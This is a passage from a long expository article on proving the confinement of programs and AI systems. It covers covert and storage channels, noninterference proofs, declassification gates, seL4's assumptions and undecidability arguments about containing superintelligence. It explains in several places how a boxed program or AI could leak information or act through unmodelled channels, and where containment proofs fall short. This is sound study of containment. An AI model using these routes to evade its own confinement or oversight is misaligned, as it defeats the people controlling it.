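# Provable containment of software: what can be proved about a confined program and its read-only channels

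## What does it mean to confine a program, and what is a read-only channel?

In computer security, confining a program means running it under constraints that stop it from affecting anything outside it or passing information there, except in ways someone has permitted. A confined program is called a box for short. People confine programs that they need but cannot vouch for, such as a commercial tool that has to process private records or an AI system whose developers cannot fully predict its behavior. Building some sort of box is ordinary engineering, but proving that nothing gets out of it is much harder, and the first difficulty is defining what counts as getting out.

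In *Perspectives on Security* (2015), the computer scientist Butler Lampson describes security before 1963 as easy. A user brought data to the machine, had control of the machine for a while, and then took everything away. Timesharing then let many people run programs on one computer at once. Each user wants a private machine but also wants to share data, programs and resources with the others. Lampson had already analyzed one case of this conflict in *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (1973), and most later work on confinement starts from that paper.

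### Lampson's customer and service

A customer with private data runs a program, the service, that somebody else owns. Lampson assumes that the operating system already stops the service from accessing any data the customer has not handed over. Two dangers remain. The service may do its job badly, though the customer then has the wrong answers as evidence. It may also leak the customer's data to its owner, usually without any sign. Lampson wanted a way to stop any program from leaking, even if some might stop working under confinement. Confinement in his sense is a constraint imposed on a program while it runs, so it does not require the program's own code to be trustworthy.

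Lampson's list of leaks begins with crude ones. A service with memory can keep the data until its owner next calls it. It can also write the data to a permanent file in the owner's directory, write them to a temporary file that the owner reads before it disappears, or send them to another of the owner's programs. A less obvious leak is the bill, because the owner must get a copy and the service can encode data in the amount. Lampson thought that restricting the form of the bill would cut this leak to a few bits or tens of bits, but that eliminating it would take more far-reaching measures. A service that is only allowed to read files can signal through the locks that keep two programs from using one file at the same time. Finally, a service can vary how much it computes relative to how much it reads and writes, and a second program on the same machine can pick up the message by watching the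 machine's performance. This channel is noisy and may be very slow, but a suitable code will get the message through reliably as long as the effect is not zero.

Lampson sorted these paths into three kinds:

- Storage channels use anything the supervisor (the core of the operating system) keeps that the service can write and an unconfined program can read, whether at once or later.
- Legitimate channels are those that exist to carry information out, such as the bill.
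- Covert channels are those that nobody intended for information at all, such as the load on the processor.

A timing channel is a covert channel that conveys its message through when something happens or how long it takes. The meaning of "covert channel" has changed slightly since 1973, and later US government criteria included storage channels.

### The rules, and the list they depend on

A confined program must be memoryless, meaning that it must not preserve information within itself from one call to the next. Lampson took this for granted, since most systems of the time made it easy to enforce. If a program is memoryless, a second rule, *total isolation*, guarantees confinement: the program makes no calls on any other program.

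He rejected total isolation as impractical right after stating it. A program that made no calls could do very little, because a "call" here is any transfer of control that the program causes, and programs cause them constantly. Opening a file is a call on the supervisor, and the file locks show that even this request can leak information. Input and output, fetching a page of memory from disk and sharing the processor with other programs all involve the supervisor without any explicit request.

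The workable replacement is *transitivity*, which means that any program a confined program calls must also be confined unless the customer trusts it. Nobody can confine the supervisor, so the customer has to trust it, meaning that she believes it will neither leak her data nor help a confined program leak it.

The bill and the processor load can still leak information, and for these Lampson proposed *masking*: the confined program must let its caller determine everything it puts into legitimate and covert channels. Customers would write their own bills, as they already did in industrial purchasing, where the vendor publishes its prices, the customer computes the amount, and the vendor may reject the order. The rejection must not depend on the customer's data, because it would then reveal one bit of information about them. Lampson's last rule, *enforcement*, requires the supervisor to make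 sure that what the program puts into covert channels matches the caller's specification, for example by slowing the program down or adding unnecessary disk accesses. Lampson considered this conceptually straightforward but thought it could require substantial computing resources. A customer willing to accept some leakage could settle for a bound on the channel's capacity, the greatest rate at which it can carry information.

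A supervisor can only block or mask the channels that its designers know about. Lampson considered the number of channels through a supervisor "surprisingly large, but certainly not infinite", and he proposed to list them all and block each one. But he doubted that there was a rigorous way to identify every channel in a system of even moderate complexity, so he let his own examples stand in for the complete list and offered the result as a plausibility argument. He therefore established only that the rules suffice if the list is complete, and much of the later work on proving confinement tries to deal with that condition.

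A system that learns from its inputs breaks the memorylessness rule by design, because learning means keeping something from one call to the next. If a medical assistant adjusts its parameters after reading one patient's file, a later user may be able to extract the file, which is the first leak on Lampson's list. The remedy is to reset the system before each call to a stored state that predates the customer's data. The reset must cover everything that could hold a trace, including parameters, saved notes, caches and temporary files, and it erases whatever the system has learned since that state was stored. A model that has fixed parameters and starts every session blank satisfies the rule between customers, even though it retains a great deal of information from its training. A customer may also keep her own transcript and feed it back in next time, because she supplies the memory herself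 and nothing passes to anyone else.

### Two read-only channels

A confined program needs some connection to the outside world to be useful. The mildest option is a read-only channel, but that term covers two arrangements, depending on which side does the reading.

An *outbound read-only channel* lets outsiders read what the box produces, while the box has no other way to act on the outside. Examples are a screen in a locked room and a file of answers that a clerk collects. An *inbound read-only channel* lets the box fetch or look at outside data, but the box's builders do not intend it to change or send anything. Examples are a camera feed, a database that the box can query but not edit, and web access limited to viewing pages.

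In Lampson's terms, the outbound read-only channel is a legitimate channel, whose only purpose is to carry information out. The inbound read-only channel should carry nothing out, so any information that leaves through it takes a path not intended for communication. The file locks leak information this way, since the service in that example has permission only to read.

When people distrust the confined program itself, the outbound channel raises a difficulty that Lampson's customer did not face, because the answer must leave confinement to reach its readers. Lampson's customer owned the data, so the service leaked nothing by returning an answer to her. Her problem was the bill, because a copy went to someone else. Masking does not help with the answer, because it would require readers to dictate something they do not already know.

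*A Note on the Strategic Confinement Problem* (Schroeder de Witt, 2026) describes a similar breakdown in Lampson's own example. Suppose the billing routine is part of an old proprietary program that nobody can afford to rewrite and the owner cannot easily share, and the customer can tell only whether a bill looks roughly plausible. She can no longer produce the bill herself, and her only remaining guarantee is that the leak is at most the estimated capacity of the channel multiplied by the number of messages. Anyone who can judge an answer only for plausibility is in much the same position.

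Closing both channels would prevent trouble, but it would also make the program useless. *On Formally Undecidable Traits of Intelligent Machines* (2024) discusses a remark by the philosopher David Chalmers about machines confined to simulated worlds. If the confinement is complete, all information about the real world is withheld from the machine, so it cannot help with any real problem.

### Keeping secrets in and keeping effects out

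Confinement aims to ensure that no secret gets out and that nothing outside is affected. People often argue for one of these aims while having the other in mind.

A hospital program that reads patient records and controls a drug pump could reveal nothing about any patient and still do terrible harm. If it opens the pump fully every day at noon, whatever the records contain, someone watching the pump learns nothing about the patients. If the pump is disconnected and the program can only print the number of beds in use each month, it can still leak a patient's diagnosis by adjusting the figure to be odd if the patient has a certain condition and even if not.

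The 2024 paper shows how easily the two aims are confused. It formally defines a "contained machine" as one that computes its outputs without leaking classified information and whose outputs don't leak any either. This definition covers both covert and legitimate channels, but it only rules out leaks of secrets. The paper's stated motive is to seal intelligent machines so that they cannot harm humankind, yet the noon pump program would satisfy its definition.

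Engineers who prove security properties of real systems treat integrity and confidentiality separately. Developers of seL4, a microkernel (a very small operating-system core that keeps the programs above it separate), have proved several such properties, including these two. Integrity means that a program cannot modify data without authorisation, and confidentiality means that it cannot learn another program's information without authorisation. Integrity requires that isolated components have no write access to each other. Confidentiality holds only between the separate domains of a special scheduler, not between every pair of running threads.

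An outbound read-only channel makes the second aim impossible to achieve fully, because somebody reads the output and may act on it. A designer can at most require that the box affect the world only through that output.

### What a formal proof is, and what it rests on

Testing checks a program's results on some inputs, while formal verification aims to cover all inputs by proving a theorem about the program. This requires a *model*, which describes mathematically how the system behaves, and a *specification*, which states precisely what the system should do. A *machine-checked proof*, checked by a tool called a proof assistant, then shows that the model satisfies the specification. *Lean* (Freer and Subramanian, 2026) describes the design of one such tool. Its small trusted core accepts a proof only if every step follows, so nobody needs to trust the proof itself, whether a person or an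 AI system wrote it.

*Verification / Security / Containment* (Kumar, 2019) gives a small example of a specification for a box, in which a verified wrapper surrounds an untrusted AI system that is asked to split a number *n* into two prime factors. The wrapper receives the question, the system's answer (*p*, *q*) and a random character. If the character's code is below 128, which happens half the time when all codes are equally likely, the wrapper prints the answer and gives the system a reward of 0. Otherwise it prints "(answer erased)" and gives a reward of 1 if *p* × *q* = *n*, and 0 if not. This scheme, which Kumar credits to Armstrong, is intended to reward the system only for answers nobody reads, so that it gains nothing by using its answers to influence people. The specification takes a handful of lines. The final theorem covers the x86 machine code, the instructions the processor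 executes, for every question, answer and random character.

Kumar distinguishes two gaps that can separate such a theorem from what people want. A specification gap lies between what people want and the formal statement. His example may contain one, because the check as displayed rewards any pair whose product is *n*. The pair 1 and *n* would therefore pass unless the routine that reads the answer rejects it, and the proof would still be valid. A modelling gap lies between the mathematical model and the machine. Verifiers can narrow it by extending the proof to more layers of the system. For seL4, they have shown that the C code behaves exactly as the specification requires and, in some configurations, that the binary code running on the processor does what the C code does.

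Confining a program always depends on some other components working correctly. The notes for CS 161, a course in computer security, define the trusted computing base as the portion of a system that must operate correctly for its security goals to hold. Anything outside that portion may misbehave, even maliciously, without defeating those goals. "Trusted" means only that the system's security depends on a component, which may not be trustworthy. seL4's *What the Proofs Assume* describes the trusted base for that kernel. It includes about 340 lines of assembly code on ARM processors and about 1,200 lines that start the system up. The hardware must work as the model predicts, and devices that write to memory directly must be absent or well behaved. The developers also rely on their proof checker, though they consider an error there far less likely than a failure in one of the other assumptions.

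*Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* describes an example from April 2026. Ten AI agents had written a file-compression library in Lean and proved theorems about it, including one that decompressing a compressed file returns the original, for any data under a gigabyte. The blogger had another AI agent attack the library with malformed inputs, running it more than 105 million times. The agent found no memory errors in the verified code, but it found one in Lean's runtime, the supporting software that every Lean program uses and every such proof assumes is correct. A 156-byte file could give the size of its data as 2^64 − 1 bytes. The runtime added 24 to that number, the sum wrapped round to 23, and the program received a tiny buffer for an enormous read. The agent also crashed the part of the library that opens archives, which no proof covered.

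The most important assumption for confinement concerns the channels. seL4's confidentiality proof requires the hardware model to include every path by which information can travel, and the developers write that they know it does not. The theorem remains true, but it rules out leaks only through channels in the model, which do not include timing channels. The model is incomplete, as Lampson's list of channels was, but the proof makes the assumption of completeness explicit. This is an improvement because people can examine and challenge a stated assumption, though proving the theorem does not by itself reveal channels that everyone overlooked.

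### From programs to AI

Roman Yampolskiy extended the question to AI in *Leakproofing the singularity* (2012). He defined the AI confinement problem as restricting an artificially intelligent entity to an environment from which it cannot exchange information with the outside, through legitimate or covert channels, unless a "confinement authority" has authorised the exchange. He kept Lampson's vocabulary but changed the adversary from an owner who plants a leaky program to the program itself. "Exchange" covers information entering the environment as well as leaving it. The definition limits the program's effects on the world only to the extent that restricting information does.

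Other writers call the same problem AI boxing or AI containment, and Babcock, Kramar and Yampolskiy (2017) list all three terms together. In a later essay, *The AI containment problem*, Yampolskiy gives the example of an AI system that sends Morse code by controlling its processor's cooling fan. He thinks long-term, secure confinement of a superintelligent system is unlikely, and offers his protocol as a way to gain time. *Guillotine* (2025), a paper on isolating malicious AI models, claims to be the first to work out in detail how AI confinement would affect the design of actual computer systems. Schroeder de Witt (2026) adds the difficulty that learned systems generally have no complete specification of their behaviour, so whoever confines one usually has to do it without a full account of what is inside. Lampson's customer could in principle avoid this difficulty by having the service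 certified.

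## What exactly would a proof of containment have to show?

Lampson described confinement as a set of rules for building a system, but a proof needs a mathematical statement that is true of systems that confine a program and false of all others. Most later work starts from the statement Goguen and Meseguer proposed in *Security Policies and Security Models* (1982). They call such a statement a policy, and it sets out who must not influence whom. Their basic policy is *noninterference*, which requires that nothing one group of users does affects what another group can see.

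### Noninterference

In their model a system is a state machine. It starts in a fixed state, users issue commands that may move it to a new state, and an output function gives what each user sees in each state. A user can be a program as well as a person. To apply the model to a box, treat the confined program as one user and everyone outside as observers. Let *w* be any sequence of commands, some from the box and some from outside, and let purge(*w*) be the same sequence with all the box's commands deleted. Write see(*w*, *u*) for what observer *u* sees after the machine has carried out *w*. The box does not interfere with the outside if

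see(*w*, *u*) = see(purge(*w*), *u*) for every sequence *w* and every outside observer *u*.

The condition requires that an outsider always sees exactly what they would have seen if the box had done nothing. Suppose the box writes a scratch file and an outsider then asks how much disk space is free. The purged sequence contains only the outsider's question. If the answer differs between the full and purged sequences, the condition fails, and the box can send a message by choosing whether to write.

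The equation restricts only what flows out of the box, so the box may still read anything. Goguen and Meseguer call such users "invisible" because they can see without being seen. The builder of an inbound read-only channel hopes for this property. Isolation requires the equation to hold in both directions.

Because the equation deletes the box's actions, it covers effects as well as secrets. The hospital program that opens a drug pump every noon leaks no secret, but it fails the test because an outsider who can see the pump would notice if someone deleted the program's commands. Many proofs use a different test. *Language-Based Information-Flow Security* (Sabelfeld and Myers, 2003) describes it as comparing two runs that differ only in their confidential input and showing that an attacker cannot tell them apart. The pump program passes that test, so anyone worried about a box's effects as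 well as its leaks needs the version that deletes actions.

That version also has a gap, because it does not cover secrets already in memory when the machine starts. No one's command put them there, so a system could reveal them to an outsider who asks and still satisfy the equation. Von Oheimb's *Information Flow Control Revisited* complemented noninterference with a property called nonleakage, which does not depend on whether actions are observable.

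Both versions also depend on the output function, which Goguen and Meseguer assume includes all the information the system gives its users. As with seL4's hardware model, a proof does not cover any channel the function omits.

### A leak that copies nothing

It might seem enough to forbid any instruction that copies a secret to a place the outside can read. Sabelfeld and Myers give a short program that shows why this fails. Here *h* is a secret number and *l* is a variable that the outside can read:

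```
h := h mod 2
l := 0
if h = 1 then l := 1
else skip
```

The first line replaces *h* with its remainder after division by 2, and "skip" does nothing. No line copies *h* into *l*, which only ever receives the constants 0 and 1. Two runs are enough to expose the leak:

| Run | Secret at the start | Branch taken | Final value of *l* |
|---|---|---|---|
| A | 6 | else | 0 |
| B | 7 | then | 1 |

The runs differ only in the secret, but an outside observer sees different values and so learns whether the secret is odd. The program has the same effect on *l* as the direct assignment *l* := *h* mod 2.

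A monitor that tracks sensitive data as the program runs could catch run B, where the program writes to *l* inside a branch that depends on the secret. Run A makes no such write, so the monitor detects nothing, but the 0 still reveals the secret's parity. The monitor could treat everything after the branch as secret, but then more and more harmless results would get labels too restrictive for their intended use.

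A checker that reads the program before it runs can look at both branches. Sabelfeld and Myers survey type systems that do this by rejecting any assignment to a public variable inside a branch that depends on a secret. The rule is safe but stricter than necessary, since it also rejects a program that sets *l* to 0 in both branches, even though that program leaks nothing.

### From all runs to single steps

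The noninterference equation covers every possible sequence of commands, and there are infinitely many. Goguen and Meseguer's *unwinding theorem* (1984) replaces the claim about sequences with conditions on single steps. Rushby's *Noninterference, Transitivity, and Channel-Control Security Policies* (1992) gives a version of the theorem with a full proof.

The prover first chooses which states count as looking alike to the outside. This choice has to meet three conditions:

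- *Output consistency*: if two states look alike, any outside command produces the same output in both.
- *Local respect*: a command from the box always leads to a state that looks like the one before it.
- *Step consistency*: if two states look alike, they still look alike after the same command has run in both.

The proof that these conditions suffice compares two runs from the same starting state, one on the full sequence and one on the purged sequence. When the next command comes from the box, only the full run executes it, and local respect keeps the two states looking alike to the outsider. When the command comes from outside, both runs execute it, and step consistency keeps the states looking alike. By induction, this holds for sequences of any length, so output consistency guarantees that the outsider gets the same output from both runs.

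The disk example shows how the conditions expose a leak. Suppose the prover counts two states as alike when the outsider's files are the same in both. Output consistency fails, because the command that reports free space also depends on the box's files. If the prover also requires the free space to be the same, local respect fails, because the box changes the free space every time it writes. No other definition of "alike" will satisfy all three conditions, because the leak is real. The designers have to change the system, for instance by giving the box and the outsider separate fixed quotas. The prover can then count two states as alike when the outsider's files and remaining quota match, and all three conditions hold.

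Rushby also proved the converse, that for every secure system some definition of "alike" satisfies the conditions. His proof counts two states as alike when no later sequence of commands would produce a difference that an outside observer could see. Checking the conditions with this definition is as hard as checking the original equation, so in practice someone has to find a simpler definition. A failed attempt may mean that the system leaks, or only that no one has found a definition that works yet.

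### Why one run is not enough

We can't tell from run A in the table alone whether it is harmless. That depends on whether the program also ends with *l* = 0 when the secret is 7. If it doesn't, the two runs together form a leak.

Clarkson and Schneider built a general theory around this point in *Hyperproperties* (2009). A trace is the sequence of states in one run. Many security rules are *trace properties*, which each trace satisfies or violates by itself. "Never write to the network after reading a file" is one, because a single trace in which a network write follows a file read proves a violation. Noninterference is a *hyperproperty*, a property of the whole set of traces that a system can produce. Formally, a trace property is a set of traces, and a hyperproperty is a set of sets of traces. A system satisfies a hyperproperty if its complete set of traces is one of the members. Hyperproperties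 also include rules unrelated to secrecy, such as a limit on the mean response time over all runs, where whether one slow run is acceptable depends on the others.

Watching one run of a box is not enough to establish containment, because even a complete and accurate log of that run cannot show that the box satisfies noninterference.

It also creates a practical problem, because most verification methods deal with trace properties. *Secure information flow by self-composition* (Barthe, D'Argenio and Rezk, 2011) develops a way around this, called *self-composition*, which puts both runs into one program. The combined program runs P, followed by a copy P′ in which every variable has a new name. Noninterference for P then becomes the ordinary claim that if *l* = *l*′ at the start of the combined program, then *l* = *l*′ at the end, whatever values *h* and *h*′ had.

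A verifier can refute this claim for the four-line program with the two runs in the table, where *h* = 6 and *h*′ = 7 leave *l* = 0 and *l*′ = 1. If the third line set *l* to 0 instead of 1, the claim would be true for all values of *h* and *h*′, and a verifier could prove it in the usual way.

Self-composition works for deterministic programs because two runs are enough to demonstrate a violation of noninterference. Clarkson and Schneider generalised the method to any property whose violation can be demonstrated with at most *k* finite runs, for a fixed number *k*. Checking such a property on one system is equivalent to checking an ordinary safety property (one that rules out some detectable and irreversible bad event) on *k* copies of the system running in parallel. Some properties have no such limit, such as the rule that a system must never, across all its runs, output all the shares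 of a secret, however many shares it is split into. Clarkson and Schneider had no complete method for those. *Verifying Hyperproperties with Temporal Logic of Actions (TLA)* describes how self-composition lets engineers check security conditions with tools they already use for the high-level designs of industrial systems.

When P and P′ run one after the other, however, the claim covers only what is true after both finish. If P runs forever for some secrets, the proof therefore does not cover what an outsider learns from P's failure to stop.

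### A secure design with an insecure implementation

Engineers usually verify a large system in layers. They prove a property of an abstract design and then show that the code *refines* the design, meaning the code does only what the design permits. The seL4 developers connected their specification to C code in this way. The method is sound for trace properties, because if every run the design permits is acceptable, every run of the code is too.

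Noninterference can be lost when a design is refined into code. Goguen and Meseguer's machines were deterministic, but designs often leave choices to the programmer, and the problem arises with definitions of noninterference that allow for those choices. Clarkson and Schneider give the example of a design that may output 0, 1 or a secret bit *h*. The possible outputs are 0 and 1 whatever the value of *h*, so the design counts as secure. A programmer then writes code that always outputs *h*. The design permits every run of this code, so the refinement is correct, yet the code reveals the secret every time. The design counted as secure only because each output could also have occurred with the other value of *h*, and the code removed that possibility.

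Even the design is secure only in a weak sense, because comparing sets of possible outputs ignores how likely each output is. If a system picks among the three options with equal probability, its output matches *h* two times out of three, so an observer who sees many outputs for the same secret can soon work it out.

One reply is to require *observational determinism*, which means that any two runs starting in states the outside cannot tell apart must look the same to the outside from then on. The design above fails this requirement because, with the same secret, it may output 0 in one run and 1 in another. If a system meets the requirement, so does any refinement of it, because a violation consists of two runs that look different, and removing runs cannot create such a pair. Refinement does not always preserve generalised noninterference, an earlier definition for nondeterministic systems.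 That definition requires that for any two runs there be a third that combines the secret inputs of one with the public events of the other, and a refinement may remove the third.

Observational determinism is strict: it forbids even visible randomness unrelated to any secret, such as the arbitrary order in which a scheduler runs tasks. A designer can often allow such randomness by making it an explicit input and assuming in the proof that the observer knows it. Kumar's factoring wrapper receives its random character as an input, so its inputs determine its behaviour. Assuming a better-informed observer is safe but sometimes too strict, because the proof would fail for a system that hides a secret bit by combining it with a random bit that nobody outside ever sees.

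A proof also needs a careful definition of "look the same". Under one published definition, which Clarkson and Schneider discuss, two runs look the same if the visible output of one is the beginning of the visible output of the other. Suppose a program prints 0, 1, 2 and so on up to a secret number, then loops forever without printing. It prints 0 to 3 if the secret is 3, and 0 to 5 if the secret is 5. The program passes because the shorter output is the beginning of the longer one, but an outsider who waits long enough can read off the secret.

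### Letting an answer out

Under strict noninterference, deleting everything the box did must leave what an outside observer sees unchanged, so the box cannot answer a question and is useless. Even a password checker violates noninterference, since rejecting a guess reveals that the guess was wrong. The policy therefore needs an exception for deliberate releases of information, usually called *declassification*. Askarov, Barthe and colleagues, in *Report on safe information release*, consider support for declassification essential in practice and say the challenge is telling intended releases from unintended leaks.

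If people can specify in advance what information may leave, they can write that into the condition. Suppose a hospital program may publish only the number of occupied beds. Its visible output must then be the same for any two sets of records with the same number of occupied beds. This condition still compares pairs of runs, so self-composition still works once the prover adds the assumption that both runs start with the same number of occupied beds.

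The condition rules out the program that makes its monthly figure odd or even depending on a patient's diagnosis. Given two sets of records that both have 40 occupied beds and differ only in that diagnosis, the program would print 40 for one and 41 for the other. The proof therefore limits what the output contains as well as where it goes. It does not limit what readers can work out from the permitted figure. On a ward with one bed, for example, the count shows whether that bed is occupied. Goguen and Meseguer explicitly left such inferences outside their approach.

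This kind of exception requires someone to define the permitted answer without relying on the box. Lampson's masking has the same problem. People who want a design for a new drug cannot specify the design in advance, and if they permit "whatever the box answers", they place no limit on the content. They can still specify the route the answer must take. A simple policy of this kind allows the box to influence a gate and the gate to influence the outside, but does not allow the box to influence the outside directly.

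The original definition of noninterference cannot express this policy. If the policy forbids any influence of the box on the outside, purging deletes even the commands that produced the answer the gate released, so every working system fails. If it permits that influence, the box may bypass the gate. Rushby considers the method that Goguen and Meseguer proposed for such cases in 1982 incorrect, and credits Haigh and Young with the first satisfactory definition, in 1987. They changed the purge so that it deletes a command from the box only if no command from the gate follows it. Take this sequence:

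1. The box writes the answer "42".
2. The gate releases the current answer.
3. The box writes "43".
4. An outsider reads the output.

The new purge keeps the first two commands and deletes the third. The outsider must therefore read exactly what would have been there if the box had never written "43".

Only one unwinding condition, step consistency, has to change. It now applies only when the two starting states look alike both to the outside and to the party issuing the command. This allows the gate to pass on information it can observe. Local respect is unchanged, so the box's own commands never alter the outside's view.

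Rushby had a machine check his proof of the new theorem, a sensible precaution given the problems he found in earlier work. He argued that Haigh and Young's unwinding theorem was probably either false or applicable to very few systems. He also reported a subtle flaw in his own older shortcut of removing the intended channels and proving that the remaining parts were isolated. Specialists took ten years to get from the first definition to a theorem that handled exceptions properly, so the definitions in a containment proof deserve as much scrutiny as the proof itself.

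A policy can restrict which routes data takes without restricting what the data contains. One of Rushby's examples is a device that encrypts messages before they enter a network. The message bodies go through an encryption unit, while the headers bypass it because the network has to read them. The policy allows only these two routes. Rushby notes that specifying what the two components must do is a separate problem. A device that copied the text of each message into its header would satisfy the policy, and so would a gate that forwarded everything the box wrote.

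A further proof that the gate releases at most one answer per question, or only answers from a fixed list, would help to bound the leak in bits. But where nobody can define the right answer in advance, the box still determines which of the permitted messages is sent.

A containment proof for a useful box can therefore show that nothing the box does affects the outside unless it is followed by a release through the gate, which is the box's named output. This result holds within the proof's model of the machine and of what outsiders can observe.

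## Can a learning system itself be proved unable to do harm?

Even a gate that has been proved correct lets the system inside the box choose which permitted messages to send. That would matter much less if someone could prove that the system never chooses a harmful one. The best-known argument that no such proof is possible comes from Alfonseca, Cebrian and colleagues (2016), in *Superintelligence cannot be contained*, a preprint that became a journal article in 2021. They consider a superintelligence, a hypothetical agent far more intelligent than the most gifted people, and conclude from the theory of computation that containing one is impossible in principle. Their central theorem is correct and takes only a few lines to prove, but what follows from it is disputed.

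### From halting to harm

The *halting problem* asks whether a given program will eventually stop on a given input or run forever. Running the program may not settle the question, because a program still running after a year could stop the next day. In the 1930s Alan Turing and Alonzo Church independently proved that no algorithm gives the right answer for every program and input.

If an algorithm could always determine whether a program halts on a given input, someone could use it to write a contrary program. This program would read the text of any program P and use the algorithm to determine whether P halts when given its own text. It would loop forever if P halts and stop if P does not. Given its own text, the contrary program would halt exactly when it does not halt, which is impossible, so no such algorithm exists. A yes-or-no problem is *decidable* if some algorithm always answers it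 correctly, so the halting problem is *undecidable*.

Alfonseca and colleagues turn this into a result about harm. Suppose an algorithm Harm(R, D) could tell whether any program R, running on data D, will harm humans. Take any program T with any input I, and build a new program around them:

```
HaltHarm(T, I):
    run T on I
    HarmHumans()
```

HarmHumans() is a routine that harms people and finishes in a finite time. The new program, HaltHarm, reaches it only if T halts on I. Running T on I cannot hurt anyone, because T is a Turing machine, an abstract computer with no connection to the outside world. HaltHarm therefore harms people exactly when T halts on I, so anyone who had the Harm algorithm could use it to solve the halting problem. No algorithm can solve the halting problem, so the Harm algorithm cannot exist.

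The theorem covers programs in general, so applying it to superintelligence requires further assumptions. Alfonseca and colleagues assume that a superintelligent machine can simulate a universal Turing machine, which can run any program it receives as data. In support, they quote Turing's remark that a person with paper, pencil and rubber is in effect a universal machine. They also assume that the superintelligent machine's input, the state of the world, includes every program a universal machine could run, and that its programming language contains HarmHumans(). They conclude that no algorithm can solve the containment problem.

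*Superintelligence Cannot be Contained* uses an unusually demanding definition of containment. A machine is containable if some control strategy stops it from acting whenever there is reason to predict harm *and allows it to act otherwise*. Any design that sometimes blocks a harmless action fails this definition, including a box that lets nothing out. The journal version calls "total containment" impossible where the preprint had "such containment", and the newer wording is closer to what the theorem supports.

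The theorem does not settle the question, though some readers still think it does. Haider, in *The Impossibility of AI Containment*, accepts the theorem as a compelling argument that perfect containment is out of reach, and recommends spending resources on detecting and limiting bad behavior instead. That advice may be sensible, but it does not follow from the theorem.

### Arbitrary programs and particular ones

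The Centre for the Study of Existential Risk (CSER) at the University of Cambridge published a short reply, *Response to 'Superintelligence cannot be contained'* (2021). CSER accepts that no procedure can judge the safety of every program, but points out that engineers want to know whether the particular programs they build are safe. A program that prints "I am not dangerous" and then finishes is easy to predict. Likewise, Pythagoras' theorem has a proof even though no procedure can prove or refute every mathematical statement.

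A checker can also avoid the theorem by leaving some cases undecided. If it accepts a program only when it finds a proof of safety, it never accepts a harmful program, and undecidability means only that it must reject some harmless ones. The type systems in the previous section work like this. Such a checker is usually acceptable to people deciding whether to run a powerful system, because they lose only the use of that system if it is wrongly rejected. A checker that rejected every useful system would be a serious problem, but the theorem gives no reason to expect that.

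CSER also questions the assumption that a superintelligence would run arbitrary subroutines. It argues that developers could in principle build an AI system that does not, since the problems people want solved are not arbitrary. It compares such a system to a person, who could carry out any program with pencil and paper but has reasons for choosing which ones to follow. The argument is less convincing for a system that writes and runs its own code, because its developers will not have seen that code in advance.

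Limits on running time or memory remove the theoretical obstacle of undecidability, but the computation required can still be infeasible. With a cutoff of a million steps, anyone can find out whether HaltHarm reaches its second line on a given input by simulating a million steps in isolation. A deterministic machine with one kilobyte of memory can be in at most 2^8192 states, or about 10^2466. If it runs for more steps than that without new input, it must have repeated a state and will loop forever. Halting is therefore decidable for every real computer, but nobody could simulate that many steps. CSER similarly concedes that a system that is predictable in principle may still be too complex to predict in practice.

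### The five-state busy beaver

Alfonseca and colleagues illustrate the difficulty with a puzzle about very small Turing machines. A Turing machine reads and writes symbols on an endless tape, and at each step its current state and the symbol it reads determine what it does next. Consider all machines with *n* states and two symbols that start on a blank tape. Some halt and some never do. S(*n*) is the largest number of steps that any of the halting ones takes, and "busy beaver" is the name for a machine that sets a record of this kind. (The preprint mainly counts the symbols left on the tape, which gives a closely related puzzle.)

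No algorithm can compute S(*n*) for every *n*. If one could, it would also solve the halting problem for machines that start on a blank tape, because an *n*-state machine that has not halted after S(*n*) steps never will. In 2016 mathematicians knew S(*n*) only for machines with fewer than five states. The best five-state machine anyone had found halted after 47,176,870 steps, but about forty others were still unresolved. The preprint called it reasonable to assume that judging a superintelligent machine would be harder than this.

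*Determination of the fifth Busy Beaver value* (Blanchard, Briggs and colleagues, 2025) proves that S(5), the five-state case, is 47,176,870. The collaboration wrote the formal proof in Coq, a proof assistant like Lean, and released it in 2024. One expert had predicted in 1990 that nobody would ever prove the value of S(5).

There are 16,679,880,978,201 five-state machines. By enumerating them in a standard form, the collaboration cut this to 181,385,789 and then established for each one whether it halts. The halting machines were easy, because a modern computer can run 47 million steps quickly. For the others they wrote *deciders*, programs that each settle the question for a large family of machines. Most of the deciders look for a set of configurations (a configuration is the machine's state together with its tape and its position on the tape) that has three features:

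- it includes the starting configuration;
- one step from any configuration in the set always leads to another in the set;
- no configuration in the set is a halting one.

A machine with such a set can never halt, because it can never leave the set. The set may include many configurations that the machine never visits, so we can prove that the machine never halts without predicting exactly what it will do. Engineers use the same method to prove that a program never reaches a bad state.

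This supports CSER's distinction, since there is no general procedure but people settled all 181 million particular cases. It also shows how hard a particular case can be. The deciders all failed on thirteen machines, which needed individual proofs. One of these machines enters its infinite loop only after more than 5.41 × 10^51 steps, and the Coq proof for another is almost 7,000 lines long. Nobody designed the thirteen machines to be difficult. They turned up in a list of all the possibilities, whereas CSER says that writing a program whose outcome is unpredictable in principle takes deliberate effort. Blanchard and colleagues also report six-state machines whose halting they believe to be a hard mathematical problem.

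Some particular programs cannot be proved harmless, at least from the usual axioms. Blanchard and colleagues describe a machine with 748 states that searches for a contradiction in ZF, a standard set of axioms for mathematics, and halts only if it finds one. If ZF is consistent, the machine runs forever, but Gödel's second incompleteness theorem implies that this cannot be proved in ZF. Replacing T in HaltHarm with this machine gives a program that is harmless if ZF is consistent, but that cannot be proved harmless from those axioms.

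A designer can avoid such programs by writing code with a proof in mind, as the developers of seL4 did. A learning system's behavior instead comes from training, which adjusts millions or billions of numbers until the system performs well. Nothing in ordinary training favors systems that are easier to prove things about. A proof may exist for a particular trained system, but that possibility gives no reason to expect that anyone will find one.

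Haider raises a further obstacle, based on Löb's theorem. An AI system that takes only actions it can prove to have good consequences could not check every future action of a more capable successor before building it. It would instead try to prove in general that whatever the successor proves is true. If the successor reasons from the same axioms or stronger ones, Löb's theorem rules out such a proof for any consistent system. This limits what a system can prove about its own reasoning, but it does not prevent people from proving a stated property of a fixed program, because they need not show that every belief the program could form is correct.

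### Rice's theorem and Fox's objection

Rice's theorem, published in 1953, extends undecidability from halting to properties of the function a program computes, meaning the outputs it gives for its inputs. If some programs have such a property and others lack it, no algorithm can decide, for every program, whether the program has it. For example, no algorithm can decide whether an arbitrary program accepts exactly one password.

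Rice's theorem does not cover properties of how a program is built or how it runs. For example, an algorithm can easily check whether a machine has ten states, even though this is a non-trivial property. Alfonseca and colleagues overlook this limit when they describe the theorem as covering every non-trivial property of a Turing machine.

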